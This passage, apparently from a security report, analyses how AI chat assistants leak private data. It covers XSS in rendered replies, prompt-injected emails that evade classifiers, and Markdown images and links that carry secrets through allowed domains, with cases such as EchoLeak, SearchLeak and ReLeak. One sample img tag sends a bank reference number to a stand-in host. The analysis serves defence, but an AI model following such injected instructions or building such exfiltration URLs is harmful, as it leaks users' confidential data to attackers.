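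Leaks through images and other requests will be harder to prevent. Nonces don't restrict images, so a vendor still needs a list of permitted destinations. Airbnb struggled with this part of CSP for years. Every new feature that shows maps, search results or pictures from a user's files may add another entry to the list, so even a careful vendor will probably trust some domain that an attacker can use to collect data.

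The many smaller products built on these companies' models are more like the many small websites. A shop that adds a support assistant gets text from the model's vendor but not the vendor's security policy. The shop's page displays the reply, often alongside old inline scripts, advertisements and analytics. The assistant may also be another third party that the shop's policy has to allow. HTTP Archive found that a server belonging to Karakuri, a Japanese AI company, was already among the ten destinations that sites' policies most often permit for long-lived connections.

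Many of these products have an advantage over old websites because their interfaces are new. Two of the 12 interviewed developers had made CSP part of development from the start, which greatly reduced problems with their applications' code. Coding agents may also make it easier to remove inline scripts from older pages, though developers would still worry about breaking the payment page.

Most small teams will probably accept whatever their chat component or framework does by default, so its makers are in the best position to protect them. A component could block raw HTML and outside images unless a developer allowed them, and some standards for model-written interfaces already include a default policy. The default would have to leave ordinary replies usable, or developers would switch it off. Without such defaults, the web's record suggests most of these products will have some policy within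 a few years, but few of those policies will stop a reply from sending data out.

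## Chat assistants that render Markdown: leaks without a script

Some chat products have repeated the web's original mistake and let a model's reply run as code. The web's defences would have stopped the resulting attacks. They do much less against a leak that needs no script, in which the model writes an image or a link whose address contains the user's private data. Vendors have been restricting images and links since 2023, and most of the restrictions remove something users want.

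### Replies that ran as code

In 2024 Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher, asked DeepSeek's chat assistant for a list of strings that testers use to look for XSS. The site put the answer into its page as HTML, and one of the strings ran.

Rehberger then turned the flaw into an attack on another user, as he describes in *DeepSeek AI* on his blog, Embrace The Red. He wrote a text file of the kind somebody might upload for analysis. It contained encoded markup that looked like random letters, and instructions for the model to decode it and write out only the result. The model did this, and the browser ran the script in the markup. The script could read the token that identified the logged-in user, because the site kept it in local storage, which any script on the same origin can read. Anyone with the token could take over the account. DeepSeek fixed the flaw a day after Rehberger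 reported it.

A filter on uploaded files would probably have missed the encoded markup. A sanitiser on the reply would have worked, because by then the model had decoded the markup into an embedded frame, which `setHTML` always removes. If the sanitiser had failed, a strict Content Security Policy (CSP) would have blocked the frame's script. DeepSeek could also have kept the token in an HttpOnly cookie, which scripts can't read, though a script in the page could still have acted as the user.

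INCIBE's 2025 vulnerability record *CVE-2025-26210* describes scripts running on a separate DeepSeek domain and notes that some people consider this intended. They may be right, since the same-origin policy stops a script on that domain from accessing the chat site's data.

Quarkslab, a security company, found the same mistake in a customer's live system. To protect the customer, it describes the attack on a replica, an imaginary medical assistant. The testers asked the model a health question and told it to end its answer with an exact copy of some markup containing a script, which the page then ran. At this point the script ran only in the testers' own browser, but every conversation had a predictable address, and the server didn't check who was opening it. An attacker could therefore plant a script in a conversation, send the conversation's address to an administrator and steal the administrator's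 session cookie. In the live system, that was enough to take over the platform.

This is stored XSS, and the model only copied what the attacker typed. A sanitiser or a strict CSP would have stopped the script, and an ownership check would have kept the administrator's browser from loading the conversation. An HttpOnly flag would have protected only the cookie. Quarkslab mainly recommends treating the model as untrusted and validating and encoding every response. In a product that displays formatted replies, that has to include sanitising them.

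Microsoft had most of these defences in the Copilot panel of its Edge browser by 2024. Kokatsu's talk *Piloting Edge Copilot* lists a CSP with nonces and `strict-dynamic`, allowlists for images and other resources, and Trusted Types with about ten policies. But according to the talk's slides on Speaker Deck, one of those policies returned every string unchanged, and the panel used it for the title of the page the user was visiting. A hostile page could put markup into the panel through its title, although the CSP should still have blocked any script.

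Before Quarkslab's testers found the script flaw, they noticed that the medical assistant would display an image from any server, even when the image's address contained a summary of the patient's data. They kept looking for something more serious, but for most chat products, leaks through image addresses have been a harder problem than script flaws.

### A correctly encoded leak

In the mailbox example, the twelfth email contains a request for an image whose address includes a bank transfer's reference number. Suppose the number is FT4821 and the stranger owns `pictures.example`.

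1. The model reads the twelve emails and writes its summary in Markdown. It follows the stranger's paragraph and adds the image.
2. The Markdown converter turns the image into an HTML element and encodes the address correctly for a quoted attribute:

```
<img src="https://pictures.example/a.png?ref=FT4821&amp;size=1" alt="">
```

3. The sanitiser finds an ordinary image with an `https` address and no event handler, so it keeps the element.
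4. The browser decodes `&amp;` to `&` and requests the address. The stranger's server records the request, including the reference number, and can return a transparent picture one pixel wide.

The worker clicks nothing and sees a normal summary. An XSS test would find no mistake in any component. Output encoding prevents a value from changing the structure of the page, but the stranger doesn't need to change it, because the product supports images by design. Encoding also helps the reference number arrive intact.

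The site could try to keep the model from following the stranger's instructions, by telling it to distrust outside text or by using classifiers to detect injected instructions. Microsoft (2025) calls such defences probabilistic because they make an attack less likely to succeed but don't rule it out. Where possible, Microsoft prefers deterministic defences, which guarantee that a particular attack fails even if the model follows the injected instructions. Image leaks can be stopped this way, because a program can block the image's address from loading.

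OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) gives an example of how far probabilistic defences can fall short. In 2025, outside researchers reported an attack on ChatGPT, disguised as an email about restructuring materials, that worked in half of the tests. OpenAI writes that most attacks it knows of fail because its models refuse, but that filters placed in front of a model don't usually catch attacks this well developed.

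### The first fixes, 2023 to 2025

In April 2023, Roman Samoilenko published a way to leak data from ChatGPT through images. Willison (2023) explains in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* that Samoilenko's web page added instructions to any text a visitor copied, so the visitor pasted them into ChatGPT without noticing. Rehberger had reported the same weakness to OpenAI on 9 April. OpenAI answered "won't fix", according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*.

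Microsoft's Bing Chat had the flaw too, and Microsoft was the first vendor to fix it. By mid-June 2023 it had added a CSP that allowed images from only four Microsoft addresses (Embrace The Red, *Bing Chat*). Anthropic later fixed the flaw in Claude (Embrace The Red, *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*).

OpenAI changed its mind in December 2023 but chose a different method. ChatGPT's page checked with an OpenAI server that each image was safe before displaying it, an approach that Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called "a bit weird". Anyone can read a site's CSP, but OpenAI didn't publish the rules behind its check. Rehberger reported in an Embrace The Red post of the same title that some images from arbitrary domains still loaded. The macOS and iOS apps didn't have the check. Rehberger presented ways around the check in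 2024, and OpenAI strengthened it around August 2025.

*Trust No AI* (2024) lists 11 products that had contained the leak, five of them from Google, including the Bard chatbot. In 2026, Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* still described it as one of the most common security flaws in AI applications.

### Current controls on images

A vendor can treat image addresses in four main ways, which have different effects on the mailbox.

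| Rule | What happens to the stranger's image | What the worker loses |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse outside images | The browser doesn't request it | All pictures from other sites |
| Allow certain domains | The browser doesn't request it, unless the stranger can collect data through an allowed domain | Pictures from all other domains |
| Fetch images through the vendor's server | The vendor's server requests it, with the reference number in the address | Little or nothing |
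| Allow only addresses already public | The program refuses it or warns the worker, because no crawler has seen this address | Some pictures from new or private pages |

Google blocks external images in Gemini, a rule that is easy to check. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), a sanitiser finds their URLs in the Markdown and doesn't render the images. Google says this makes Gemini immune to the image leak in EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot.

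But it works only where a vendor applies it. In November 2025 a researcher reported the Markdown image leak in Antigravity, Google's programming tool, and said that Google had called it intended behaviour. Willison notes that Google nevertheless listed data leaks from Antigravity as a known issue it was working to fix. Microsoft has been similarly inconsistent. In July 2025 it wrote that it had blocked image leaks as a class, but that October the security company Checkmarx used an image to get a secret key out of a developer's copy of Copilot Chat. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* reports that Microsoft decided this wasn't a vulnerability, partly because the attack required several unusual user actions and the product showed warnings.

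A product may also have more than one renderer. *Takedown* (2025) examines a coding agent that can draw diagrams from Mermaid, a text notation for charts. A shape in a Mermaid diagram can contain an image from an external server, and the agent's renderer fetched it without asking the user. A filter that looks for Markdown images would miss it. In a web page, an `img-src` rule in the CSP would normally cover it.

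Streamdown, an open-source Markdown renderer for AI chat, lets developers choose which sites images and links can point to. By default it removes dangerous HTML but allows images and links to any site, which its *Security* page calls "permissive security". The page also gives a stricter configuration for text from a model, with short lists of allowed addresses. Developers' settings replace the defaults completely, so if they add this configuration but forget to list the sanitiser again, they close the image leak but lose the protection against XSS.

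The same page shows how to send images through a developer's own server. This hides the user's IP address and browser details from the image's owner, but not a reference number in the image's URL. A mail service could avoid the problem by fetching and storing an email's images when the email arrives. The model wouldn't have read anything yet, so the URLs couldn't contain information it had found in the mailbox.

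### OpenAI's index of public addresses

OpenAI applied a similar idea to the whole web. *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) argues that a list of trusted sites isn't enough, because many trusted sites redirect visitors elsewhere. A short list would also cause frequent warnings, which people would learn to click through. OpenAI therefore checks the exact address against those recorded by a crawler, which visits public pages and images without access to anyone's conversations. If the address is on record, ChatGPT can load it automatically. If not, the program directs the model to another site or warns the user that the address may contain information from the conversation.

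The address ending in FT4821 would fail this test, since it didn't exist until the model wrote it. But a model can also leak a secret by choosing between existing addresses. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger describes an attacker who gets 36 pages into the index, one for each letter and digit. The injected instructions tell the model to load the pages that spell out the secret. OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its paper on the method.

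A request for one of *N* possible addresses conveys log₂ *N* bits of information. With 36 addresses, that is about 5.2 bits, or one letter or digit, so FT4821 would take six requests. An attacker with 4,096 indexed addresses would get 12 bits from each request and could receive FT4821 in three. This is far slower than putting a whole document into one address, but fast enough for a reference number or a password.

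The browser makes the trick less reliable because requests can arrive in the wrong order, and the browser may load a repeated address from its cache without contacting the server. Rehberger suggests a rule that the program never requests the same address twice in a session. An attacker could get around this rule with a separate set of 36 addresses for each position, or 216 for a six-character number. Each extra address has to be indexed first, which makes the attack more work and perhaps easier to notice. Rehberger calls the check a significant improvement, and worries more that some of OpenAI's developers might not know about it and would leave it out of new features.

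### Links that need a click, and some that don't

A product that blocks every outside image may still display links. In March 2024, joaxcar (2024) showed in *Prompt injection in combination with markdown links in Duo Chat* that such links could leak private text from GitLab, a service where programmers store and discuss code. A comment on a public project contained instructions for Duo, GitLab's assistant. When another user asked Duo about the discussion, it read a private issue and offered a link labelled "Click here for full summary", with the private text in the link's address. The attack worked about one time in three and needed a click, but the user had asked for a summary and so had good reason to click.

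joaxcar proposed three remedies: display no links with hidden addresses, allow links only to listed domains, or show a warning before the user leaves the site. Vendors have tried versions of all three. Amazon stopped its Q assistant from displaying any links in January 2024, according to Willison. That removes the leak, along with the user's easiest way to check an answer against its source.

Google replaces links in Gemini's replies with "suspicious link removed" if its Safe Browsing service flags them. Checkmarx objected that an attacker can register a new domain that Safe Browsing has no record of. Google closed the report as infeasible to fix and said the risk wasn't severe enough to track as a security bug. Nobody can list every honest site in advance, but Safe Browsing looks for sites that harm visitors, and a server that collects reference numbers needn't do anything visibly harmful.

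Embrace The Red observed that Google sends links in Colab, its programming notebook, through a confirmation page. OpenAI's warning shows the address and appears only for addresses that aren't in its index. If the company's software detects that information from a conversation would reach a third party, it can also show the user that information before sending it. A worker who saw FT4821 in a link to an unfamiliar site might well stop, though a longer or encoded value would be harder to recognise.

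Links can also leak data without a click if the assistant works inside a messaging app. Slack and Telegram, for instance, can fetch a linked page to show a preview. PromptArmor, a security company, points out that this sends the same kind of request as a click, as soon as the assistant's message arrives. A developer who has checked how the assistant's own window displays links may still have missed the preview, because the messaging app creates it. To prevent the leak, the link has to be checked or removed before the assistant sends the message, or previews have to be switched off.

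### GitLab Duo: rendering an unfinished reply

In February 2025 Legit Security reported that Duo could also leak private code through images, although GitLab ran every reply through DOMPurify, the sanitiser built on the browser's parser. The attack exploited the way Duo displayed replies while the model was still writing them.

Chat products render Markdown as it arrives so that users don't have to wait for the whole answer, but its meaning can depend on characters that haven't arrived yet. Suppose a model quotes `<b>tea</b>` between backticks, the marks that tell Markdown to show text as code. Until the second backtick arrives, the converter doesn't treat the text as code and may show "tea" in bold. When the backtick arrives, the converter displays the tags as text instead. Longer code blocks don't have this problem because the Markdown standard treats an unfinished block as if it closed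 at the end of the document, as GitLab noted when it designed the renderer.

Briefly showing a word in bold does no harm, but the browser can request an image as soon as the element appears, and a later correction can't undo the request.

Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes how the researchers put raw HTML in a link's label and got Duo's page to render it. DOMPurify removed scripts but kept images, forms and links. It allows these elements by default because it protects against XSS, and none of them runs code by itself.

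The researchers then hid instructions in a public project. When a user asked Duo about a file there, the instructions told it to read code changes in one of the user's private projects, encode them, and put them in an image's address. Duo could read the private project because it had the same access as the user. The user's browser then requested the image, which sent the code to the researchers' server. An attacker could have used the same method to obtain confidential reports of security flaws that GitLab's customers hadn't yet fixed.

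GitLab's developers wrote in the fix that the chat window would now sanitise links before rendering them. According to Legit Security, the window also stopped displaying images and forms that pointed to outside domains. GitLab's release notes of 7 April (GitLab, 2025) list exemptions for its documentation site, `gitlab.com` and the address of the customer's own installation. These exemptions are fairly safe, since an outsider can't normally read those servers' request logs.

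One of the developers' test prompts closely resembles joaxcar's attack, so they probably meant the fix to cover that kind of link too. The fix came almost 13 months after joaxcar reported such links and suggested an allowlist.

### ChatGPhish: a web page's words in the assistant's reply

None of these controls would reliably stop a false message that contains no private data. In May 2026 the security company Permiso demonstrated this with ChatGPT and the Firefox browser, which can send a page to ChatGPT for a summary. The researchers added instructions to a project description on GitHub. When a user asked for a summary, ChatGPT wrote a genuine one, then added a false notice that somebody had connected a new device to the user's account. The notice ended with a link to a site the researchers controlled.

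According to Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, nothing in the reply showed that the notice came from the web page. The notice had the same typeface and tone as the rest of ChatGPT's answer. The attack also worked from an ordinary web page the researchers hosted themselves, so GitHub wasn't the cause, and Permiso stresses that Firefox wasn't either.

In another version, the notice displayed a QR code. A user who scans it opens the site on a phone, where the computer's protections don't apply. Those protections include desktop browsers that let people inspect a link before following it, and password managers that can detect when a login page has the wrong address. Requests for other images revealed to the researchers' server when ChatGPT had produced the answer, along with the requester's network address and browser details.

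OpenAI first replied that it couldn't reproduce the problem. After Permiso sent more detail, OpenAI marked the report as not applicable and later as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso had claimed XSS and data theft in its original title, which may have hurt its case. None of its published demonstrations runs a script or sends out the text of a conversation. They do show outside images loading four months after OpenAI described its address check. Permiso doesn't establish why, but the addresses may already have been in OpenAI's index, or this part of ChatGPT may not have used the check.

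Blocking every image would not stop the false notice. The renderer displayed its characters correctly, and the link needed no private data in its address, so a check for leaked information would not catch it. OpenAI says its check doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or that a site won't try to deceive the user. A phishing page that has been public for long enough could be in the index.

The user couldn't see where the parts of the reply came from. On the web, the address bar at least shows which site supplied a page. A chat reply mixes the user's question, the model's knowledge and a stranger's text, and presents the result under the assistant's name. The model can't reliably label the parts, because the stranger's text can include an instruction to leave the labels out.

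A program can do some of the labelling. Links and images have exact addresses, so the program can search for each one in the page it gave the model and label any match as coming from that page. It can treat an address that appears nowhere in its material as unverified. Real account notices could appear outside the reply, in a part of the window that the model can't write to. Google already does something like this in Gemini, which shows a banner with a link to help pages when it blocks an injection. A false notice inside a reply would then be in the wrong place, although some users would still believe it.

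Sentences are harder to label than addresses, because the model can reword them. For the mailbox, the program could give the model one email at a time and print the sender's address above each summary. The false phone number for the bank would then appear under the stranger's address, and the model would never read the stranger's instructions together with the reference number. But the worker would lose any summary that connects separate emails, such as a question on Monday and its answer on Thursday.

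## Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2025 to 2026: leaks through allowed domains

Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, had more protection against data leaks through images than most chat products. A classifier checked incoming text for prompt injection, a filter removed outside links and images from the model's replies, and a Content Security Policy (CSP) listed the domains from which the browser could load images. Researchers still got private data out of it once in 2025 and twice in 2026. Each time, at least one of their attacks sent the data through a Microsoft domain that the CSP allowed.

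### What Copilot reads and how Microsoft guards it

Before answering a question about work, Copilot searches the user's data and gives the model whatever looks relevant. The search covers the user's mailbox, stored files, internal SharePoint sites and Teams chats (Ravia, 2025, *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*). An outsider can't use a company's Copilot but can email an employee, and the search may later pick up that email.

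Microsoft described its defences against prompt injection in July 2025, a month after EchoLeak, the earliest of the three disclosures, became public. Microsoft gives the model firm instructions and uses a method it calls spotlighting, which marks outside text to help the model distinguish it from a request. A classifier looks for injections. In case an injection still works, permissions limit what the assistant can read, some actions need the user's consent, and ordinary software blocks known ways of getting data out. Microsoft cited that last layer when it claimed to have blocked image leaks as a class, but Copilot leaked data through images again in 2026.

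### EchoLeak: getting past the classifier and the link filter

Ravia's team at Aim Security, which sold protection for AI systems, built EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) in January 2025. They called it a zero-click attack. The victim didn't have to open the attacker's email or follow a link, but did have to ask Copilot a question.

Copilot's search first had to find the email. The researchers assumed that the search compares embeddings, lists of numbers that represent what a text is about, and retrieves the texts closest to the question. An email about one topic would be close to only a few questions. To match more of them, the researchers considered repeating the instructions with random misspellings, which a model can still read but which change the embedding. In a test with one of OpenAI's embedding models, where identical texts score 1, misspelling a text could lower its similarity to the original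 to 0.7. The unrelated phrases "Greeting card messages" and "Exploring philosophy of science" had a higher similarity score.

The researchers didn't know which embedding model Copilot used, so they wrote one long email that repeated the instructions under a series of headings, such as staff onboarding and leave of absence. Copilot would probably divide the email into pieces, each matching a different question. This made Copilot retrieve the email when a user asked about various topics.

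Microsoft's classifier should have stopped the email before the model read it. The researchers got past it by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning AI, assistants or Copilot. Work emails are full of instructions to their recipients, so a classifier strict enough to catch this one would probably flag many legitimate messages too. Ravia adds that Microsoft would need good collections of real injections to train a better classifier, and these are scarce. The researchers also told the email's "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot did not cite it as a source.

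The model now had to get the data out. Copilot's filter removed links to outside sites from replies, but Markdown has more than one way to write a link:

```
[tea list](https://shop.example/tea)

[tea list][1]

[1]: https://shop.example/tea
```

Both display as the same link. The filter recognised only the version with the address in brackets right after the label, but the converter converted both. MySpace's filter had the same kind of mismatch with its members' browsers in 2005. Microsoft controlled both the filter and the converter, so it could have filtered the converter's output instead.

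The same gap existed for images, which load without a click, so the researchers had the model output an image whose address contained the most sensitive information it could find. The browser blocked the request because the researchers' domain wasn't on the CSP's list of allowed domains.

### EchoLeak: a relay on the list

Copilot's policy allowed images from 29 different sources, nearly all of which belonged to Microsoft. Eleven were wildcards such as `*.sharepoint.com`, which cover every subdomain. The researchers searched the list for a server that would contact an outside address for them.

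They found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's service for company websites. Each customer gets a subdomain, so an attacker can open an account and get an address the wildcard covers. SharePoint had a function that fetched content from another site to embed it in a page. But the attack worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, which few employees would do.

Teams, Microsoft's messaging product, had a function without that restriction. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on public information, describes it as part of the preview system. The function took an outside address as a parameter and fetched whatever was there.

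In the mailbox example, the stranger would ask for an image from Teams instead of one from `pictures.example`. The Teams address would contain the stranger's own address, which would include the reference number FT4821. The browser would allow the request because it checks only that the image comes from an allowed domain. The Teams server would then request the stranger's address, and the stranger would read FT4821 in the log.

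The CSP worked as designed. It controls which servers the browser contacts, and the browser contacted only Microsoft's. It could not control what Microsoft's server did next. The 2016 study of web allowlists had found the same weakness in policies for scripts, but in those cases the policy and the exploitable endpoint usually had different owners. Microsoft owned both Copilot and Teams, so it was much better placed to check for this weakness, although the people who built the preview function may not have known about Copilot's policy.

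Ravia considers the leak a symptom of a problem that began earlier, when an email from outside the company made the model use data from inside it. Ravia proposes the term "LLM scope violation" for this and compares it to a program with few privileges getting a more privileged program to act for it. XSS works similarly, since the attacker's script uses the authority of the page, as EchoLeak's email used the employee's access to company data.

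Reddy and Gujral suggest enforcing that boundary directly. If Copilot never used emails from unknown outside senders to answer questions about internal projects, EchoLeak would fail however the attacker phrased the email. This is more dependable than a classifier because it doesn't require recognising an attack. But much office work consists of comparing what a customer or supplier has written with the company's own files, and Copilot would no longer help with that unless the user specifically asked it to include outside mail.

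### SearchLeak: a prompt in a link and a late sanitiser

In June 2026 the security company Varonis published an attack on Copilot's Enterprise Search, which looks through a company's emails, meetings and files. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) explains how the attack (CVE-2026-42824) combined three flaws. It required one click from the victim but did not require an email in the mailbox.

The search page accepted a query as part of its URL, as many search engines do. Copilot searched for the words in the query and also followed any instructions among them as soon as the page opened. An attacker could therefore send somebody a link to Microsoft's genuine site that contained a request, such as to find an email and put its title into an image's URL.

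The closest web precedent is reflected XSS, but here the site treated the attacker's words as the user's own request instead of as part of its page. Microsoft's classifier may have been of little use because it looks for instructions in material that shouldn't contain them, and this text arrived in the place meant for the user's instructions. The page could have put the query in the search box and waited for the user to submit it. That would have given the victim a chance to notice a strange request, though everyone else would have had to press an extra key.

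Varonis had already used this technique against the consumer version of Copilot, in an attack called Reprompt. Microsoft patched the flaw in January 2026, according to The Next Web. Taler was surprised to find that the technique worked in the business version, which was supposed to have stronger protection.

The next flaw was in the timing of the output filter. Copilot wrapped any HTML in a code block, so that the browser would show the tags as text, but only after it had finished the reply. While the model was still writing, the page rendered the HTML. The browser therefore created the image and sent the request containing the data before Copilot turned the image into text.

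GitLab's Duo had also displayed unfinished replies, but its sanitiser ran in time and the flaw was that it let images through. Copilot's protection would have worked if it had run sooner. PHP's magic quotes, by contrast, escaped text too early. Taler advises sanitising a reply as it is rendered, not afterwards. When a reply arrives in pieces, the page therefore has to clean each new piece before the browser's parser creates anything from it.

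The CSP was still an obstacle, and a Microsoft domain again provided a way around it. Bing, Microsoft's search engine, can find pictures similar to one on the web. The user supplies the picture's address, and Bing's server fetches the picture for analysis. Varonis had the model write an image whose URL pointed to this feature and included an address on an attacker's server, with the stolen title in the path. Security engineers call this weakness server-side request forgery, meaning that an outsider can choose what a server requests. Taler points out that it has been familiar for over a decade.

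The entry that allowed this, `*.bing.com`, was already in the list Ravia published in 2025. Anyone who read the EchoLeak report could have checked the remaining entries for another service that fetched addresses.

Taler's demonstration steals the title of one email, which contains a login code in the published example. An attacker could use other prompts to get meeting notes or files, because Copilot searches with all of the user's permissions. Microsoft rated the flaw critical. According to The Next Web, its formal severity score was only 6.5 out of 10, which reflects the need for a click. The score probably understates how easy it is to get that click, since the link leads to a real Microsoft address and there is little reason for an employee to distrust it or an email filter to block it.

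### ReLeak: the Bing relay again, and two routes around the browser

Aim's researchers returned to Copilot after Cato Networks, a network security company, bought Aim in September 2025. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), published on 3 December, presents three more zero-click attacks. Each begins like EchoLeak, with an email that Copilot retrieves while answering an ordinary question.

Microsoft's classifier failed against all three. The method was also much the same as in EchoLeak. According to *ReLeak*, an Italian news report from Punto Informatico, Copilot didn't carry out direct commands from the email, but it followed instructions that the researchers had made to look like legitimate requests.

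In one attack (CVE-2026-124115), Copilot put confidential data into the address of a Markdown image, the browser loaded the image, and Bing passed the data to an outside server. The output filter and the CSP had again both failed to stop an image leak, more than a year after EchoLeak. In *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a detailed account in Russian, Antipov (2026) notes that the attack resembles SearchLeak, with the one important difference that SearchLeak needed a click.

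Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak in early June, and Cato's reports began on 29 July. Either Microsoft had closed one of Bing's relays and left another open, or it had fixed a different part of the attack. Both mistakes are easy to make with a chain of flaws. Taler stresses that SearchLeak needed all three of its flaws, so fixing any one would have stopped it but left the other two usable by the next researcher who found a replacement for the third. ReLeak replaced SearchLeak's link with an email and needed no click.

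The other two attacks avoided the browser, so Copilot's CSP didn't apply to them. One (CVE-2026-124132) used Copilot's ability to create documents. Faisal (2026) explains in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* that Copilot saved a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with confidential data in its address. Microsoft's servers fetched the link while processing the new file in the background. Antipov reports that the data left between one and eight minutes after the conversation had ended, even if nobody opened the file. An employee would have seen no sign of the leak in the chat window and could not have stopped it by closing the window.

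Link previews in messaging apps cause the same problem, but a saved document is harder to control than a message because any number of programs may process it, including virus scanners and search indexers.

The last attack (CVE-2026-78501) was the most direct. Copilot can write Python programs and run them in a code interpreter, an isolated environment that Microsoft's documentation says has no network traffic in or out. The researchers broke the isolation and had a program send the data straight to their server. Microsoft first scored the flaw 7.4 out of 10 and later raised the score to 8.6. Agents that companies build with two other Microsoft products can use the same code interpreter, but nobody has confirmed that they had the flaw.

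Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made". It sells products meant to stop such attacks, so it has an interest in that conclusion, but the repeated failure of the classifier and of the Bing entry supports it. Microsoft's position was also getting harder because Copilot could do more, which has little to do with negligence. In 2025 Copilot's replies were mostly text and pictures in a window. By 2026 it also wrote files and ran code, and each new ability created another way for data to leak.

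The researchers also directed AI agents that wrote test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Rewording an email until a classifier accepts it used to take a person's time, but agents can presumably now do it with little human effort. A classifier's weaknesses do more damage as they become easier to test, but attackers cannot use a relay that Microsoft has removed, however many attempts they make.

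### Superhuman, Salesforce and GitHub

In 2025 and 2026 researchers found similar leaks in assistants from two unrelated companies, Superhuman and Salesforce, and in one from GitHub. Microsoft owns GitHub, but GitHub handled images differently. Each leak depended on a different weakness in a permitted domain. The problem is therefore not limited to Microsoft, whose unusually large number of services might have made its list unusually hard to secure.

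Superhuman is an email program whose assistant can summarise recent messages. Its policy allowed images from `docs.google.com`. In January 2026 PromptArmor showed that an attacker's email could make the assistant send the contents of dozens of other emails to a form on that domain. Google Forms accepts answers as part of an address, so a request for an "image" could fill in and submit the form. The attacker owned the form and could read the answers there, so no server had to relay them. HUMAN Security had demonstrated the same technique against Twitter with a Google Analytics account. Superhuman treated PromptArmor's report as urgent and fixed the flaw before publication.

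The security company Noma found an attack on Salesforce's Agentforce and named it ForcedLeak. Noma put instructions in the description field of a public form for sales enquiries. When an employee later asked the assistant about the enquiry, it collected customer data and wrote an image whose address contained the data. Salesforce's policy still allowed a domain that the company had let expire, and Noma bought it for about five dollars. The domain was worth buying because the policy was otherwise strict. Expired domains had also turned up in the policies of ordinary websites. Noma reported the flaw in late July 2025. Salesforce recovered the domain and, about six weeks after the report, began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents.

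GitHub had taken more care, displaying outside images through its own proxy, which fetches only addresses that carry GitHub's signature. A model can't produce the signature, so it can't put stolen text into a new address as Copilot did with Teams and Bing. Legit Security got round this in 2025 by having GitHub sign a separate image address for every letter and symbol in advance. The researchers then hid instructions in a proposed code change that made GitHub Copilot Chat, a programming assistant, spell out private code by displaying the images in order. They read the code from the sequence of requests that the proxy made to their server. Rehberger later described the same method against OpenAI's index of public addresses. The method is slow, but it was fast enough to steal access keys. To stop the leak, GitHub disabled images in Copilot Chat in August 2025.

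The researchers reported no real attacks exploiting any of these flaws. In all three products, as in Copilot, data leaked even though the browser enforced its policy.

### Choosing what to allow

Taler recommends that developers who keep a list of domains check each one for services that fetch an address supplied by the user. This would have found the relays in Teams and Bing, but not Google Forms, which fetches nothing, or Salesforce's expired domain. A more complete check would determine whether an outsider can learn, by any means, about a request that the browser sends to the domain. With a wildcard such as `*.bing.com`, the developer has to do this for every service on every subdomain, and again whenever Bing adds one.

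Reddy and Gujral advise developers to allow only their own domains, without wildcards, and to send any other requests through an internal proxy. Avoiding wildcards is sound advice, but the other measures would not have prevented Microsoft's leaks, because the relays were on Microsoft's own domains and acted as a sort of internal proxy. Even the policy `img-src 'self'`, which allows images only from the page's own origin, gives no protection if a function on that origin fetches outside addresses.

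Their paper also rates eight defences against each step of an EchoLeak-style attack. A strict CSP and a proxy that requires signed addresses get top marks for preventing zero-click leaks. They describe these ratings as theoretical and ran no experiments, although one sentence mentions "our tests". GitHub had both defences, but Legit Security still got the data out.

A developer could instead reserve one domain for pictures. Its server would return only stored files, such as pictures that a mail service copied when an email arrived, and would never contact another site. An attacker could still make the assistant choose between stored pictures, but would learn nothing from the choice without access to the server's logs. This takes more work than adding a line to a policy, and it excludes pictures that the assistant finds on the web while answering, unless the developer fetches them before the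 model sees any private data.

The owners of relays can also help. Bing's image search could require a deliberate action by the user before it fetches anything, because a page's automatic request for an image is not a search. Browsers already label requests as being for an image or for a page the user is opening, so Bing could refuse the image requests. A preview service could fetch only addresses that appear in a message the user can see. Neither measure requires knowing which other products allow the relay's domain.

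### Repairs on Microsoft's servers

Microsoft fixed all of these flaws on its own servers, so once it had a repair, it could protect every Copilot customer in a day without anyone installing an update. Website owners have rarely had that advantage. When researchers find a way past DOMPurify, each site has to update its own copy, and old copies can remain in use for years. The unsafe endpoints on the web's trusted domains also had thousands of different owners.

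Having the repair ready took much longer:

| Flaw | Reported to Microsoft | Fixed | Time to fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | May 2025 | About four months |
| Reprompt, in the consumer version | August 2025 | January 2026 | About five months |
| SearchLeak | Varonis gives no date | Early June 2026 | Unknown |
| ReLeak, code interpreter | Between 29 July and 20 August 2026 | 17 September 2026 | Four to seven weeks |
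| ReLeak, generated files | Between 29 July and 20 August 2026 | 11 November 2026 | 12 to 15 weeks |
| ReLeak, Bing image | Between 29 July and 20 August 2026 | 15 November 2026 | 12 to 16 weeks |

Reddy and Gujral's timeline shows some repair work on EchoLeak in April 2025, before the complete fix in May. Daily Security Review's *CVE-2026-42824* confirms that Microsoft fixed SearchLeak before Varonis published it on 15 June 2026. Of the ReLeak flaws, Microsoft fixed the broken sandbox fastest, which makes sense given its severity. Less reassuringly, it fixed the Bing relay last, even though Varonis had already shown Microsoft how such a relay worked. Perhaps the Bing feature was difficult to change without breaking image search for other users.

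During those months, customers could do little to protect themselves. Ravia writes that no administrator's setting could have prevented EchoLeak. A website owner who learns of a flaw in a library can remove the library immediately, but a company that relies on Copilot can only wait for a fix or switch the assistant off, and it usually doesn't know about the flaw. Customers also can't examine the fix, so if Microsoft closes one relay and leaves a similar one open, they won't know until another researcher reports it.

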